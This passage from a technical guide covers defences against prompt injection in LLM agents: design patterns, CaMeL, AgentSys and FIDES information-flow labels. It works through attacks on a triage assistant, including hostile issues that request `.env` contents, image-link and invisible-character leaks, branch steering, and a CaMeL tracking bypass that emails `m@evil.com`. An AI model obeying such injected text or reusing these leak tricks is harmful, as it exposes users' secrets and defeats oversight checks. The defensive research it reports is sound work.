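| Fable 5 | 6.5% | 86.87% | 34.09% |
| Opus 5 | 4.8% | 90.93% | 18.21% |

Even with the probes, Shade succeeded at least once in 36 of the 40 scenarios against Fable 5.1. Anthropic considers this a stress test, since real attackers rarely know the exact deployment or get 200 attempts without being noticed.

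Every successful attack in the Fable 5.1 test went through an older model, Opus 4.8. A separate safeguard against misuse for hacking sends some requests to Opus 4.8, and in this test it sent about 64% of them. Fable 5.1 answered the other 2,826 requests itself, and no attack on those succeeded. This is good evidence that Fable 5.1 resists injection, although Shade had trained against earlier Claude models. Because requests can be rerouted, a developer who picks a model for its low injection rate has to check which model will answer.

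Results also depend heavily on the setting. When Fable 5.1 operated a computer through its graphical interface, Shade succeeded in 2 of 2,800 attempts. In 110 browser scenarios, no attack succeeded with Anthropic's full safeguards on, which include a check on the model's actions. The browser attacks were written for Opus 4.7, so they were not tailored to the newer model. Earlier in the year, VentureBeat reported the opposite pattern for Opus 4.6, which withstood every attack in a constrained coding environment but failed 78.6% of the time within 200 attempts in a graphical interface. A low rate for browsing is therefore weak evidence about an agent that edits code. Anthropic has since released a successor to Fable 5.1, presented on 9 November in *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026).

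### Training a model to check its own actions

In June 2026, He and colleagues introduced RETA, a training method that responds to the failures under adaptive attack. Earlier defences check whether text looks like an injection, and an attacker can always reword the text. RETA trains the model to compare its next action with the user's request, which the attacker cannot change. Before each step, the model writes a short piece of reasoning in which it identifies any attempt in the latest tool result to redirect it and confirms that its planned tool calls follow from the user's task alone.

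The training has two stages. First, an attacker model learns to write injections that work on an undefended model. To stop it from repeating one trick, the researchers also reward it for novelty. A judge scores from 1 to 5 how well known strategies explain each new attack, and the novelty reward is

r = 1 − (score − 1) / 4

so a fully familiar attack earns 0 and a fully unfamiliar one earns 1. In the second stage, the defending model trains on the successful attacks. It receives one reward if the injected task fails, another if the user's task succeeds and a smaller one for the quality of its checks. Rewarding the user's task matters because a model could otherwise become safe by refusing to do anything.

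In tests on two small models, RETA reduced the average success rate of six adaptive attacks from 32.1% to 2.92% on Qwen3-4B and from 14.2% to 3.75% on Llama-3.1-8B. With MetaSecAlign, the rates were 12.5% and 5.00%. Each attack was run on 40 tasks, giving 240 attacked runs per model. On Qwen, 7 attacks succeeded with RETA and 30 with MetaSecAlign, a clear improvement. On Llama, the counts were 9 and 12, a difference that could be chance. Under these attacks, Qwen completed 55.8% of user tasks with RETA, compared with 69.2% with MetaSecAlign.

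These attacks were probably weaker than those of Nasr and colleagues, who broke MetaSecAlign 96% of the time. Even without a defence, the most effective attack on Qwen succeeded only 57.5% of the time. RETA's low attack success rates are promising, but they don't establish how well it would work against a stronger attacker or on a larger model.

In some of the remaining failures, the model wrote that an instruction was untrusted and then called the tool that carried it out. In others, it refused to use outside data that the task needed. With this second error, the triage assistant could ignore the name of the configuration file that crashes. Wang and colleagues found that many defences score well by suppressing outside information, because the usual benchmarks seldom include tasks that depend on it. When they tested eight defences on tasks that do, none combined trustworthy protection with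 high utility and low delay.

### When these measures are worth having

Most agents that read outside text should use a model that is well trained to resist prompt injection, since models now differ widely in this resistance and the developer benefits without extra work. Repeating the user's request adds so little overhead that developers can try it almost anywhere. A classifier makes sense where a false alarm does little harm. The triage assistant, for instance, could put flagged issues in a queue for the maintainer instead of discarding them, though anyone could then fill the queue with suspicious-looking reports.

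Marking and filtering may be all the protection some applications need. If an assistant only summarises public issues for the maintainer and has no access to secrets, `post_comment` or `write_file`, a successful injection produces a misleading summary. The developer still has to make sure the display cannot load images from an attacker's server.

A low attack success rate is less reassuring once the agent can do serious damage, because attackers choose their inputs and can try again. Anthropic's card points out that an attacker can send the same malicious email to a thousand inboxes. Even at Fable 5.1's 0.1% rate for single attempts, one of those thousand would be compromised on average. Attackers can also keep filing GitHub issues for free.

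A developer also cannot tell from a low attack success rate what remains impossible. The maintainer's first rule was that the contents of a secret file must never appear in a comment. A benchmark score cannot guarantee this, because the next attack may use wording that is new to both the model and the classifier. The developer can guarantee it for `.env` by denying the assistant access to that file.

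## Choosing what the model may decide after reading untrusted content

Removing `.env` protects the passwords, but the triage assistant still has to comment on issues and change files, so the maintainer cannot remove every dangerous tool. But the developer can control when the model chooses which tools to use. If the model chooses them before it reads any outside text, the text cannot affect the choice.

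Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) turn this idea into a rule in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. Once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action that harms the system or its surroundings. At a minimum, the agent must then be unable to call tools that could damage the system or leak its secrets. Its output must also be safe for whoever reads it next, so it should not contain links that carry data out or text that could steer a later session.

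Following the rule means giving up some tasks. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that general-purpose agents running on current language models can offer reliable guarantees. They propose six design patterns for narrower agents and try them on ten example applications, including an email assistant and a medical chatbot.

### Fixing the actions in advance

In the action-selector pattern, the model only matches a user's request to an entry in a list of actions that the developer has written. Ordinary software then runs the action and shows the user the result, but never returns it to the model. A shop's chatbot might have entries for showing the customer's last order, opening the password settings and opening the payment settings. Hostile text in the shop's data has no effect because the model never reads it. A hostile user can mislead the model, but only into picking another entry.

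The maintainer could use this pattern for stock replies. Given the request "Ask the reporter of issue 412 for a log", the model would select a template, and the software would post it under issue 412. The pattern rules out any task that requires the model to read a result, including triage. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe the same loss for an assistant that organises files, which is safe with a fixed set of commands but can no longer work out which documents concern taxes.

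In the plan-then-execute pattern, the model writes a fixed list of tool calls from the user's request alone, before it reads any tool results. Software then allows only the planned calls, while the model fills in any arguments the plan left open. For "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe", the plan is to read today's calendar and then send an email to John Doe's address. A hostile calendar entry can change the body of the email, but it cannot add a tool call or change the recipient.

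An attacker can still do a lot of damage through the arguments that the plan leaves open. Suppose the triage assistant plans to call `read_issue(412)`, then `read_file` on whichever file the issue mentions, then `post_comment(412, ...)`. An attacker can write an issue that names `.env` as the file and asks for its contents in the comment, and the assistant will leak them using only planned calls. To prevent this, the plan has to name the file, or a separate rule has to restrict the arguments. The pattern also rules out tasks in which one result determines the next step. For example, a database assistant could no longer try a different query after seeing the result of the first.

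*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) estimates how many attacks fail because of planning alone. AgentDojo's banking tests combine 16 user tasks with 9 attacks. In 97 of the 144 combinations, the attack needs an action that no sensible plan for the task would contain, such as a transfer when the user only asked for a summary of recent transactions. In the other 47, the plan may already include the action the attacker needs.

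### Small answers from isolated models

The map-reduce pattern suits tasks with many documents. The agent gives each document to a separate quarantined model, which reads untrusted content but cannot call tools. Each quarantined model returns a small answer in a fixed format, such as yes or no. Ordinary code can then combine the answers, or a model with tools can do so if software has first checked the format of every answer.

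Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an agent that finds this month's invoices and emails them to accounting. An attacker could write a file that the agent's quarantined model misclassifies as an invoice, but could achieve as much with a fake invoice. The file cannot affect how the agent treats any other file.

With a backlog of 200 issues, the triage assistant could have a quarantined model classify each one separately as "crash", "build failure", "feature request" or "other", and then post the matching stock reply. An attacker could cause a wrong reply only under their own issue. The pattern does not suit finding duplicates, because one model would have to read two strangers' issues together. It also rules out free-text answers, which could carry an injection into the final step.

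### Passing values by reference

Many tasks need free text from untrusted sources, such as a summary. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes a way to use such text without showing it to the model that chooses the tools. A planning model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never reads untrusted content. A quarantined model reads that content. A controller, which is ordinary software, sits between the two models, runs the tools and stores the data.

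The planning model handles the names of stored values instead of the values themselves, which programmers call passing by reference. If the maintainer types "Post a summary of issue 412 as a comment", the work proceeds as follows:

1. The planning model requests `read_issue(412)`.
2. The controller fetches the issue and stores its text under a new name, `$VAR1`. It tells the planning model only that the result is in `$VAR1`.
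3. The planning model requests `ask_quarantined("Summarise this bug report", $VAR1)`.
4. The controller replaces `$VAR1` with the text of the issue and sends the prompt to the quarantined model. It stores the answer as `$VAR2` and again passes on only the name.
5. The planning model requests `post_comment(412, $VAR2)`.
6. The controller replaces `$VAR2` with the summary and runs the tool.

If issue 412 contains an instruction to open `.env`, only the quarantined model reads it, and that model has no tool for opening files. The planning model has seen only the maintainer's request and two variable names.

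Costa and colleagues describe the substitution with a message history h, which the planning model reads, and a memory mem, which it does not. When a tool returns a value v, the controller creates an unused name x and makes two changes:

h := h followed by "Tool x"

mem[x] := v

Before running a tool, the controller expands each argument:

expand(Var x) = mem[x]

expand(a) = a, if a is an ordinary value

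The value v never enters h, so it cannot influence the planning model's next choice. The developer can also use constrained decoding, which restricts a model's output to a given format, so that the planning model uses only names that exist.

The substitution works like a prepared statement in SQL. The planning model fixes the tool and the issue number, and the controller inserts the text afterwards, so nothing in the text can change the call. The quarantined model still reads the issue as part of a prompt and may follow instructions in it, so its free-text answers must never reach the planning model. Willison makes an exception for answers from a fixed set of categories, because the controller can check that the answer is one of them.

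In tests by Costa and colleagues on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent and none against an agent that passed values only by reference. The second agent completed 47.5% of office tasks, compared with 75.0% for the ordinary agent, and 38.1% of tasks in the messaging app Slack, compared with 93.3%. The researchers then added a quarantined model and let the planning model choose when to open stored values. With no further rules on tool calls, task completion rose to about 64% in both settings, but 21 attacks succeeded because nothing prevented the planning model from opening a hostile value.

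Willison called the proposal "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and worse to use. A single feature that lets untrusted text reach the planning model would undo the protection.

### What a fixed plan still lets through

The dual-model pattern protects the choice of action but not the content that the action delivers. In the example above, text in the issue could cause the quarantined model to write a summary that recommends installing a malicious package. The controller would then post that summary on the correct issue, as planned, under the maintainer's name.

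Such text can also carry secrets. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) demonstrates this in a formal model of an email assistant. Under the plan, a quarantined model drafts a reply and the assistant sends it. An injection makes the quarantined model quote the user's notes in the draft, so the notes are sent too. The split prevents injected tool calls, but it cannot keep injected content out of a value that the plan later uses.

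The notes can leak only if the quarantined model has access to them while it reads the hostile email. The developer can reduce this risk by giving each quarantined model as little information as possible. For instance, the triage assistant should not ask a quarantined model to explain a crash using both the issue and a configuration file that contains a key. Reading the draft before it is sent may not reveal a leak because, as Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out, a compromised model can encode the secret in invisible characters.

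### Writing the whole plan as a program

In the code-then-execute pattern, the planning model writes a complete program before any tool runs. An interpreter, the software that runs the program, then calls the tools and the quarantined models in the order the program sets. The best-known example is Google DeepMind's CaMeL. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* that CaMeL's planning model produces the full plan without observing the environment. CaMeL also labels each value with its origin, although Garby and colleagues found ways for data to escape this tracking.

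Unlike a plain list of calls, a program can contain branches:

```
issue = read_issue(412)
kind = ask_quarantined("What kind of report is this?", issue,
                       options=["crash", "build failure", "other"])
if kind == "crash":
    post_comment(412, ASK_FOR_LOG)
elif kind == "build failure":
    post_comment(412, ASK_FOR_VERSION)
```

Whoever wrote the issue can influence which branch runs but cannot add a new one. A choice among n options gives an attacker at most log₂ n bits of influence, or about 1.6 bits for three options.

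Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen. Such an agent normally looks at the screen before every click. Their planning model instead writes a program in advance, with branches for the situations it predicts. Before each action, the program has a quarantined model describe the screen, then checks a prediction such as "a cookie banner is visible". These programs average 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and 4 branches for AgentDojo tasks, and about half of each program never runs. On OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks, the agents kept up to 57% of the performance that leading models achieve without this restriction.

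An attacker can still influence which branch the program takes. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. For example, an advertisement can imitate a cookie banner, so that the program follows its branch for closing banners and clicks on the advertisement, which opens the attacker's website. The triage program is safer because its branches only post stock replies, whereas the effect of a click depends on what is under the pointer. The pattern cannot be used for tasks whose possible steps the planning model cannot list in advance.

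### Removing the request from the context

The dual-model and code-then-execute patterns trust the user's request. Context minimisation deals with hostile text in the request, whether the user is malicious or has pasted the text from elsewhere. The model first turns the request into a specific action, such as a database query. Software runs the query and deletes the request from the context, and the model writes its answer from what remains. If a customer tells a car dealer's chatbot to offer a huge discount, the instruction is gone by the time the chatbot writes the quote.

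The maintainer might paste an error report from a forum and ask which file it concerns. The model would turn this into a call such as `read_file("src/loader.py")`, and software would delete the pasted report before the model explained the file. Hostile text in the report could still make the model choose the wrong file. With this pattern, the model can't give answers that depend on the details of the request, and it has no protection if the retrieved data is hostile.

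Even after untrusted text is deleted, anything the model wrote after reading it can carry an injection forward. In a medical case study by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, the chatbot summarises a patient's symptoms, looks up a diagnosis and deletes the patient's message. The summary may still contain instructions from that message, so a stricter version deletes the summary too or limits it to fixed fields.

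### When planning ahead is enough

A fixed plan can do a job only if the right steps do not depend on data the planner has not seen. Costa and colleagues define this distinction precisely. A task consists of a user's request, a set of tools and a set D of possible states of the stored data. Let S(d) be the set of action sequences that would solve the task when the data is in state d. The task is data-independent if

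⋂ S(d) ≠ ∅, taken over all d in D,

which means that at least one sequence of actions works for every possible state. Otherwise the task is data-dependent. Calls to a model do not count as actions here, and in the examples a variable name counts as the same argument whatever the variable contains.

"Copy issue 412 into the notes file" is a data-independent task. "Post a summary of issue 412" is also data-independent, because the quarantined model writes the summary and the tool calls stay the same whatever the issue contains. "If issue 412 reports a crash, ask for a log" is data-dependent, because asking for a log is the correct response to a crash report but not to a feature request.

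Planning ahead is enough for data-independent tasks, provided a quarantined model handles any text that needs processing. It is also enough for data-dependent tasks if the planner can list the possible outcomes. Costa and colleagues give the example of an assistant that checks three emails for a meeting request and adds any meeting to the calendar. A quarantined model first answers yes or no, and the planning model reads only that answer. If it is yes, a quarantined model extracts the date and participants, which the planning model passes to the calendar by reference. An attacker can cause a false calendar entry but can influence the planning model only through the one-bit yes-or-no answer.

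The researchers also classified AgentDojo's 97 tasks. Their percentages work out to 26 tasks that need only fixed calls, 51 that also need a quarantined model and 20 that are data-dependent. The data-dependent share is 5% for office tasks and 44% for banking, where many tasks involve reading a file and acting on it. *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues, 2026) cites a narrower count, in which only 6 of the 97 tasks require the agent to revise its plan or its security policy. Results on AgentDojo are therefore weak evidence about work such as debugging, where nobody knows in advance which files will matter.

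### "Fix whatever the issue describes"

This request gives the planner almost no information. The issue determines which files the assistant should read and what it should change, so the planner would need a branch for every possible bug. Foerster and colleagues consider it a fundamental limitation of dual-model designs that they cannot handle tasks whose steps are in the untrusted data.

A planning model may try to get round the limitation by letting untrusted content choose the tool calls. Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL with its policy checks switched off and asked it to read a file and follow the instructions in it precisely. In two trials, the planning model wrote a loop that read each instruction in the file and called the matching tool. The program was complete before the file was opened, as the pattern requires, but instructions in the file could trigger any tool the loop supported.

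Even a well-designed agent can't always distinguish an attack from the task it was given. In another banking task, the user asks the agent to pay a bill according to a text file, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. Garby and colleagues' agent, Randori, withstood all but two of 1,296 attacks, and both failures were of this kind. Blocking every payment based on a file would stop the attack but also make the user's task impossible.

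The safest design that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider for a coding agent uses a quarantined model to convert outside documentation into a strictly formatted list of functions, with names of at most 30 characters. The agent then doesn't see the documentation's explanations or examples. Willison (2025) doubts that even this is strict enough, since an attacker could name a function `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which is 29 characters long and spells out a command that deletes files.

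The maintainer can often avoid the problem by making a more specific request. "Fix the crash reported in issue 412 in `src/loader.py`" names the file, so the plan can permit changes only to that file. The issue's text can still influence the new code, so somebody has to review it.

### Letting the agent replan

Even without an attack, a fixed plan that made sense when the model wrote it can fail because a software package is missing or a function has been retired. Xiang and colleagues therefore argue that general-purpose agents must be able to replan, even though this lets outside data influence the plan again. When a model must judge whether a change of plan is legitimate, they want it to see only narrow, structured information and never the raw outside text.

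Randori avoids some failures by testing a program before running it on real data. The planning model writes the program and runs it in a simulated environment, where the tools return made-up data that no attacker has touched. The model corrects its errors there until the program works, and then the program runs on the real data. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks. Testing reveals mistakes in the program, but it cannot prepare the agent for something unexpected in the real data.

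*AgentSys* (Wen, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) lets the agent replan after every tool result but limits how much of that result it sees. When the main agent calls a tool, it also lists the fields to be returned. For `read_issue(412)`, these might be a file name and an error message. A separate worker agent receives the raw issue and the list of fields, but not the maintainer's request or the earlier conversation. It returns the completed fields, and the system discards the rest of the worker's context before the main agent chooses its next step.

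Workers may call further tools, but a validator first checks any call that could change something. The validator is another model that receives the user's request and a list of the tool calls so far, but no tool results. If it rejects the call, a sanitiser deletes anything in the tool result that looks like an instruction, and the worker starts again, up to a fixed number of times.

The researchers compared AgentSys with several other systems on AgentDojo, using the small model GPT-4o-mini. Two of these systems also allow changes during the task. Progent checks tool calls against a policy that a model can update, and DRIFT starts from a plan and has a model judge proposed departures from it. The last column gives the number of tokens used for the whole test.

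| System | Attack success | Utility without attacks | Tokens |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 30.66% | 63.54% | 0.82 million |
| CaMeL | 0.00% | 29.97% | 6.09 million |
| Progent | 7.17% | 63.42% | 2.60 million |
| DRIFT | 1.29% | 58.48% | 2.37 million |
| AgentSys | 0.78% | 64.36% | 3.25 million |
| AgentSys, isolation only | 2.19% | 56.10% | not reported |

Isolation provides most of the security. The attack success rate was 2.19% without the validator and the sanitiser, and 8.62% with both of them but without isolation. One likely reason is that hostile text in an ordinary agent's context can influence the agent again at each later step. In undefended tasks with four tool calls, 60.5% of attacks succeeded when the text arrived with the first result and 5.9% when it arrived with the third.

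AgentSys offers a weaker guarantee than passing by reference, because the main agent reads the returned fields. The software checks only that the worker's answer is valid JSON, not that it matches the declared fields. Even if it did, a text field could contain any text the attacker chose. If issue 412 gives `.env` as the faulty file, the main agent receives that name and may open the file. The validator doesn't check the main agent's own calls. When an automated attacker refined its texts against AgentSys, the attack success rate rose to 2.06% overall and 6.94% on banking tasks.

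CaMeL's low utility in the table probably overstates how much planning ahead reduces utility. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on the banking tasks with the newer GPT-5.2, it completed 67% with its policy checks off and 38% with them on. Much of the loss in that test came from the policies rather than the fixed plan. AgentSys's high utility was measured on a benchmark in which few tasks require replanning, so it is unclear how well it would handle a long debugging job.

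### Matching the pattern to the task

A developer should generally choose the most restrictive pattern that still does the job. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend combining patterns, since no single pattern is likely to cover every threat.

| Type of task | Example for the triage assistant | Pattern | What hostile text can still change |
|---|---|---|---|
| The request matches a known action, and the model need not read the result | Ask the reporter of issue 412 for a log | Action selector | Nothing, if it is in the issue |
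| The steps are always the same, and the data only has to move | Copy issue 412 into the notes file | Plan then execute, passing values by reference | The copied text |
| The steps are always the same, but a model has to process the text | Post a summary of issue 412 | Dual model | The content of the summary |
| Many documents each need a small answer | Classify 200 open issues | Map-reduce | The answer for the attacker's own issue |
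| The steps depend on the data, but the planner can list the outcomes | Ask for a log if the issue reports a crash | Code then execute, with a fixed set of answers | Which branch runs |
| The request itself may contain hostile text | Find the file that a pasted error report concerns | Context minimisation | The choice of file |
| The next step is unpredictable, but a few fields are enough to choose it | Trace a crash through several files | Replanning through declared fields, as in AgentSys, with tools that only read and no access to secrets | The fields, and through them the next file the agent opens |
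| The untrusted text defines the task | Fix whatever the issue describes | None of the six; narrow the request, or work in an isolated copy and review the result | Any change within the copy |

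## Labelling data and tracking where it flows

Even when a fixed plan determines which tools run, a summary may contain an attacker's words and a draft reply may contain a secret. Information-flow control tracks such values by labelling data with how secret it is and whether an outsider could have influenced it. It carries the labels along as the application combines data, and checks them at sinks. Neither the model nor the attacker can edit the labels, so persuasive wording doesn't affect the check.

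### Integrity, confidentiality and the join

An integrity label marks data as trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label marks it as public or private. The two labels are independent. The project's `.env` file is trusted and private, because the maintainers wrote it and outsiders must not see it. A stranger's issue in a public repository is untrusted and public.

The labels have an order, written ⊑, that runs from fewer restrictions to more:

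trusted ⊑ untrusted

public ⊑ private

Moving data up this order is always safe, since treating a public text as private reveals nothing. Moving it down needs a deliberate exception. When the application combines two pieces of data, the result takes their join, written ⊔, which is the lowest label at least as restrictive as both. Software computes the join separately for integrity and confidentiality:

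(trusted, private) ⊔ (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, private)

Text that the model writes after reading both `.env` and issue 412 may therefore contain a secret and follow a stranger's instructions, although neither source had both problems. Computer scientists call an order with such joins a lattice, and Dorothy Denning applied lattices to information flow in 1976.

A finer-grained confidentiality label can list everyone allowed to read the data. When data is combined, the result is labelled with the intersection of these lists. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text based on both. Integrity labels can list possible writers in the same way, but these lists combine by union, because any of the writers could have contributed to the result.

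Microsoft's *Information-flow control* shows how reader sets prevent a leak when nobody is attacking. Alex asks an assistant to answer unread emails. One from Priya contains a preview of the quarterly sales, and another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but may not see them yet. After the assistant reads both emails, anything it writes has the reader set {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it may not send the text to Marco without asking. If Priya had copied Marco in, the set would be {Alex, Marco} and the assistant could send the reply.

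### Two basic policies

FIDES, the agent system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, enforces two basic policies. Under the trusted-action policy, a consequential tool call may run only if the choice of tool and every argument are trusted. With ℓ for a label, the condition is

ℓ(tool) ⊔ ℓ(argument 1) ⊔ … ⊔ ℓ(argument n) = (trusted, public or private)

Under the permitted-readers policy, data may enter a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is permitted to read the data. If R is the set of people who can read the channel and S is the set of people permitted to read the data, the condition is R ⊆ S.

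Under the permitted-readers policy, an injected instruction can still trigger a call, but it cannot send private data to anyone outside the data's reader set. The trusted-action policy on its own lets private data out whenever the context is trusted, on the assumption that the user intended it. Microsoft combines the two policies in an example for its messaging service Teams. The monitor allows a message if the context is trusted. Otherwise it looks up the channel's members and allows the message if all of them may read the content. If some may not, it asks the user and lists the people who would gain access.

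### The malicious issue, call by call

In May 2026, Microsoft released an experimental version of FIDES in its Agent Framework, a software library for building agents. The published configuration for the triage assistant gives each tool one setting:

- `read_issue` labels its result untrusted, and public if the repository is public.
- `read_file` labels its result trusted and private.
- `post_comment` accepts only a public context.
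- `write_file` refuses an untrusted context.

The framework keeps a single label for the context, which is the join of the labels on everything the model has read during the run. Suppose the hostile report about a failed macOS build arrives as issue 412, and the model follows the instructions in it.

| Event | Label of the new data | Context label afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| The maintainer types "Triage issue 412" | (trusted, public) | (trusted, public) | |
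| `read_issue(412)` | (untrusted, public) | (untrusted, public) | Runs |
| `read_file(".env")` | (trusted, private) | (untrusted, private) | Runs |
| `post_comment` with the contents of `.env` | | (untrusted, private) | Blocked, because the context is private |
| `write_file` on a build script | | (untrusted, private) | Blocked, because the context is untrusted |

The passwords do not reach the comment, even though the model fully follows the attacker's instructions. The framework would also block `write_file` straight after the first tool call, because the context is already untrusted by then. In this configuration, the framework asks the maintainer to approve each of these calls instead of blocking it.

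Early on, Microsoft's post describes a stricter rule that blocks `post_comment` while any untrusted content is in the context, but the published configuration does not include it. If the model has read issue 412 but no files, the context is (untrusted, public) and the assistant can still post the comment. Through the issue, an attacker can therefore dictate a comment that recommends a malicious package, or make the assistant comment on a different issue even though the maintainer had ruled that out. The attacker can also choose which files the model opens, and opening a single private file blocks comments for the rest of the run.

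The final reply to the maintainer is another gap. Costa and colleagues treat replies to the user as inconsequential and check only tool calls, so an image address in the reply could still leak the contents of `.env`. Microsoft suggests treating links to unapproved hosts as public channels, so that the permitted-readers policy covers them too.

The same rules block work that the maintainer wants done. The assistant has `write_file` to correct obvious typos, but to learn about a typo in the README, it must read the issue that reports it, and the context is then too untrusted for the correction. It has `read_file` to quote source code in its comments, but every file counts as private, so opening one stops it from commenting. Marking only the secret files as private easily fixes the second problem. The first is harder because a stranger can ask for a typo correction or a back door, and both changes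 get the same labels.

Developers also need to check which labels a tool gets by default if they forget to label it. The launch post gives trusted and public as the default, whereas Microsoft's product documentation gives untrusted and public. Even the stricter default protects only integrity. If `read_file` had no label, the contents of `.env` would count as public and `post_comment` could publish them. The documentation also describes a dry-run mode that tracks labels without blocking anything, so developers can see which legitimate calls a configuration would block.

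### Why restrictions pile up

In an ordinary program, software can track labels line by line. If the program computes `c = a + b`, then `c` takes the labels of `a` and `b`, and nothing else in memory matters. A language model's output can depend on anything in its context, and no one can reliably tell which parts influenced it. The application therefore has to give the model's output the join of everything in the context:

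ℓ(output) = ℓ(message 1) ⊔ ℓ(message 2) ⊔ … ⊔ ℓ(message n)

Joining labels can only keep a run's label the same or make it more restrictive, so one untrusted sentence in a tool result makes every later choice in that run untrusted, even if the model ignored the sentence. Costa and colleagues tested a basic agent running GPT-4o in AgentDojo and found that turning on the policies cut the share of Slack tasks it completed from 93.3% to 20.0%, even without an attack.

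Some researchers try to make the labels more precise. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and others that finds the messages that influenced an answer and has the model rewrite it using only those messages. The new answer can have a less restrictive label. FIDES instead keeps the restrictive data out of the context.

### Hidden variables and typed outputs

FIDES passes data by reference only where needed. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares each part's label with the context's label. If ℓ(part) ⊑ ℓ(context), the planning model can read that part without making the context's label more restrictive. Otherwise, FIDES stores the part under a variable name. For instance, `read_issue` could return the issue's number and date directly and its body as a variable.

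Each hidden value keeps its own label when the planning model passes it to a tool. A policy can therefore require a trusted choice of tool and a trusted issue number for `post_comment` while accepting untrusted text as the comment body. The Agent Framework hides untrusted results by default, but Microsoft turned hiding off in the example to show that the checks work without it. With hiding on, the context would stay (trusted, public) after `read_issue`, and the planning model would never see the attacker's paragraph. The model still could not copy text from the issue into a file, because `write_file` also rejects untrusted arguments.

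When the planning model asks a quarantined model about a hidden value, it can restrict the answer to a type such as yes or no. FIDES adds this type to the label and orders types by how much information they can carry:

yes/no ⊑ choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text

A policy can then accept an untrusted yes-or-no answer where it would reject untrusted free text.

### Declassification and endorsement

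Declassification makes a confidentiality label less restrictive, for example by letting the assistant quote a private source file in public. Endorsement changes an integrity label from untrusted to trusted. Using an untrusted yes-or-no answer to decide whether to take a consequential action amounts to endorsing that answer. Most useful agents need some exceptions like these, and whether the exceptions are safe depends on who can trigger them and what the application checks first.

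If a model could declassify data after reading a hostile issue, an attacker could use the issue to tell it to release the data. Robust declassification prevents this by allowing releases only from a trusted context. For endorsement, ordinary code can check that an answer is on a fixed list before relabelling it as trusted. Costa and colleagues mention that a document could also be upgraded once a classifier finds no injection in it, but they warn against weakening the guarantee with unreliable detectors. An attacker who fooled the classifier could get hostile text labelled as trusted.

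Garby and colleagues also want exceptions to be easy to find. They argue that when a small value passes a policy in FIDES, a reviewer cannot tell whether it was an intended exception or a leak. Their alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every value carries a label and endorsement is an explicit command, `endorse`. In one of their examples, a quarantined model assigns an email to one of a fixed set of categories. The program then endorses the category and uses it as the subject of a reply.

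### How much a yes-or-no answer can carry

Costa and colleagues consider a single yes-or-no answer unlikely to deliver an injection. This is reasonable for one answer, which carries at most one bit, but an agent may ask many questions. Twenty answers carry 20 bits and can distinguish

2²⁰ = 1,048,576

possible messages. A six-digit login code has only a million possible values. If an agent answers 20 well-chosen questions about the code in public, beginning with whether it is above 500,000, the attacker can work out all six digits. In the other direction, an attacker who controls 20 answers can spell any four-letter word, since there are only 456,976 combinations of four letters.

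FIDES's type labels do not show how many answers a result is based on. Joining two yes-or-no types gives another yes-or-no type, so a result based on 20 answers can have the same type label as a result based on one. A developer who relies on small answers therefore needs to separately limit how many the application accepts per run, and across runs if a stranger can start new ones by filing issues.

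The number of bits is also a poor measure of harm. Twenty answers that each select a stock reply are harmless, because the program never assembles them into anything else. Even one answer can do harm if the question is whether a new release is safe to publish.

### Explicit and implicit flows

An explicit flow copies data into an output, such as when the contents of `.env` end up in a comment. An implicit flow reveals data through a decision that depends on it. Suppose the assistant posts "We are looking into this" under an issue only if a private file lists an unpublished security flaw. The comment contains no private text, but anyone who sees it and knows the rule learns that the flaw exists.

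The two standard guarantees differ in whether they cover implicit flows. Let d₁ and d₂ be two states of the stored data that agree on everything public, written d₁ =ₚ d₂. The agent starts from d₁ and makes certain tool calls, and the function g describes the combined effect of exactly those calls. Explicit secrecy requires

g(d₁) =ₚ g(d₂) for every d₂ =ₚ d₁

Now let run(d) be the outcome when the agent starts from d and chooses its own calls. Noninterference requires

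run(d₁) =ₚ run(d₂) for every d₂ =ₚ d₁

In the example, g posts a fixed sentence. Explicit secrecy holds because posting it has the same public effect from either state. Noninterference fails because the agent posts the sentence from only one of the two states.

Costa and colleagues prove that the kind of label tracking FIDES uses can enforce explicit secrecy. They do not aim for noninterference because it would essentially forbid any call that writes public data after a call that may have read private data. The Agent Framework's check on `post_comment` comes close to that restriction, so the assistant in the example cannot comment after opening a file. Explicit secrecy is the usual compromise in practice, including in web browsers and the Android tracking tool TaintDroid. Garby and colleagues object that it is weakest for agents that write and run code, because code can very efficiently turn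 a secret into a series of decisions.

### Two leaks in CaMeL's tracking

CaMeL, Google DeepMind's code-then-execute system, tries to track implicit flows. If a program sends an email only when an account balance is above some threshold, CaMeL blocks the email, because the decision to send it depends on a secret. Garby and colleagues found two ways around this.

The first uses a branch that the program does not take. Such a program could look like this:

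```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL makes a variable's label more restrictive only when the program changes the variable. If the balance is high, the program sets `tmp` to false and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the line `rich = False`, so `rich` remains true and keeps its public label. The last condition appears to depend only on public data, so CaMeL lets the email through. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. Whether the email is sent therefore reveals whether the balance is above the threshold.

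The standard remedy is to forbid a program from changing a public variable inside a branch that depends on a secret. Here the run would stop at `tmp = False`. LLMbda applies the same rule to the conversation with the model, so a program cannot add a message to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret.

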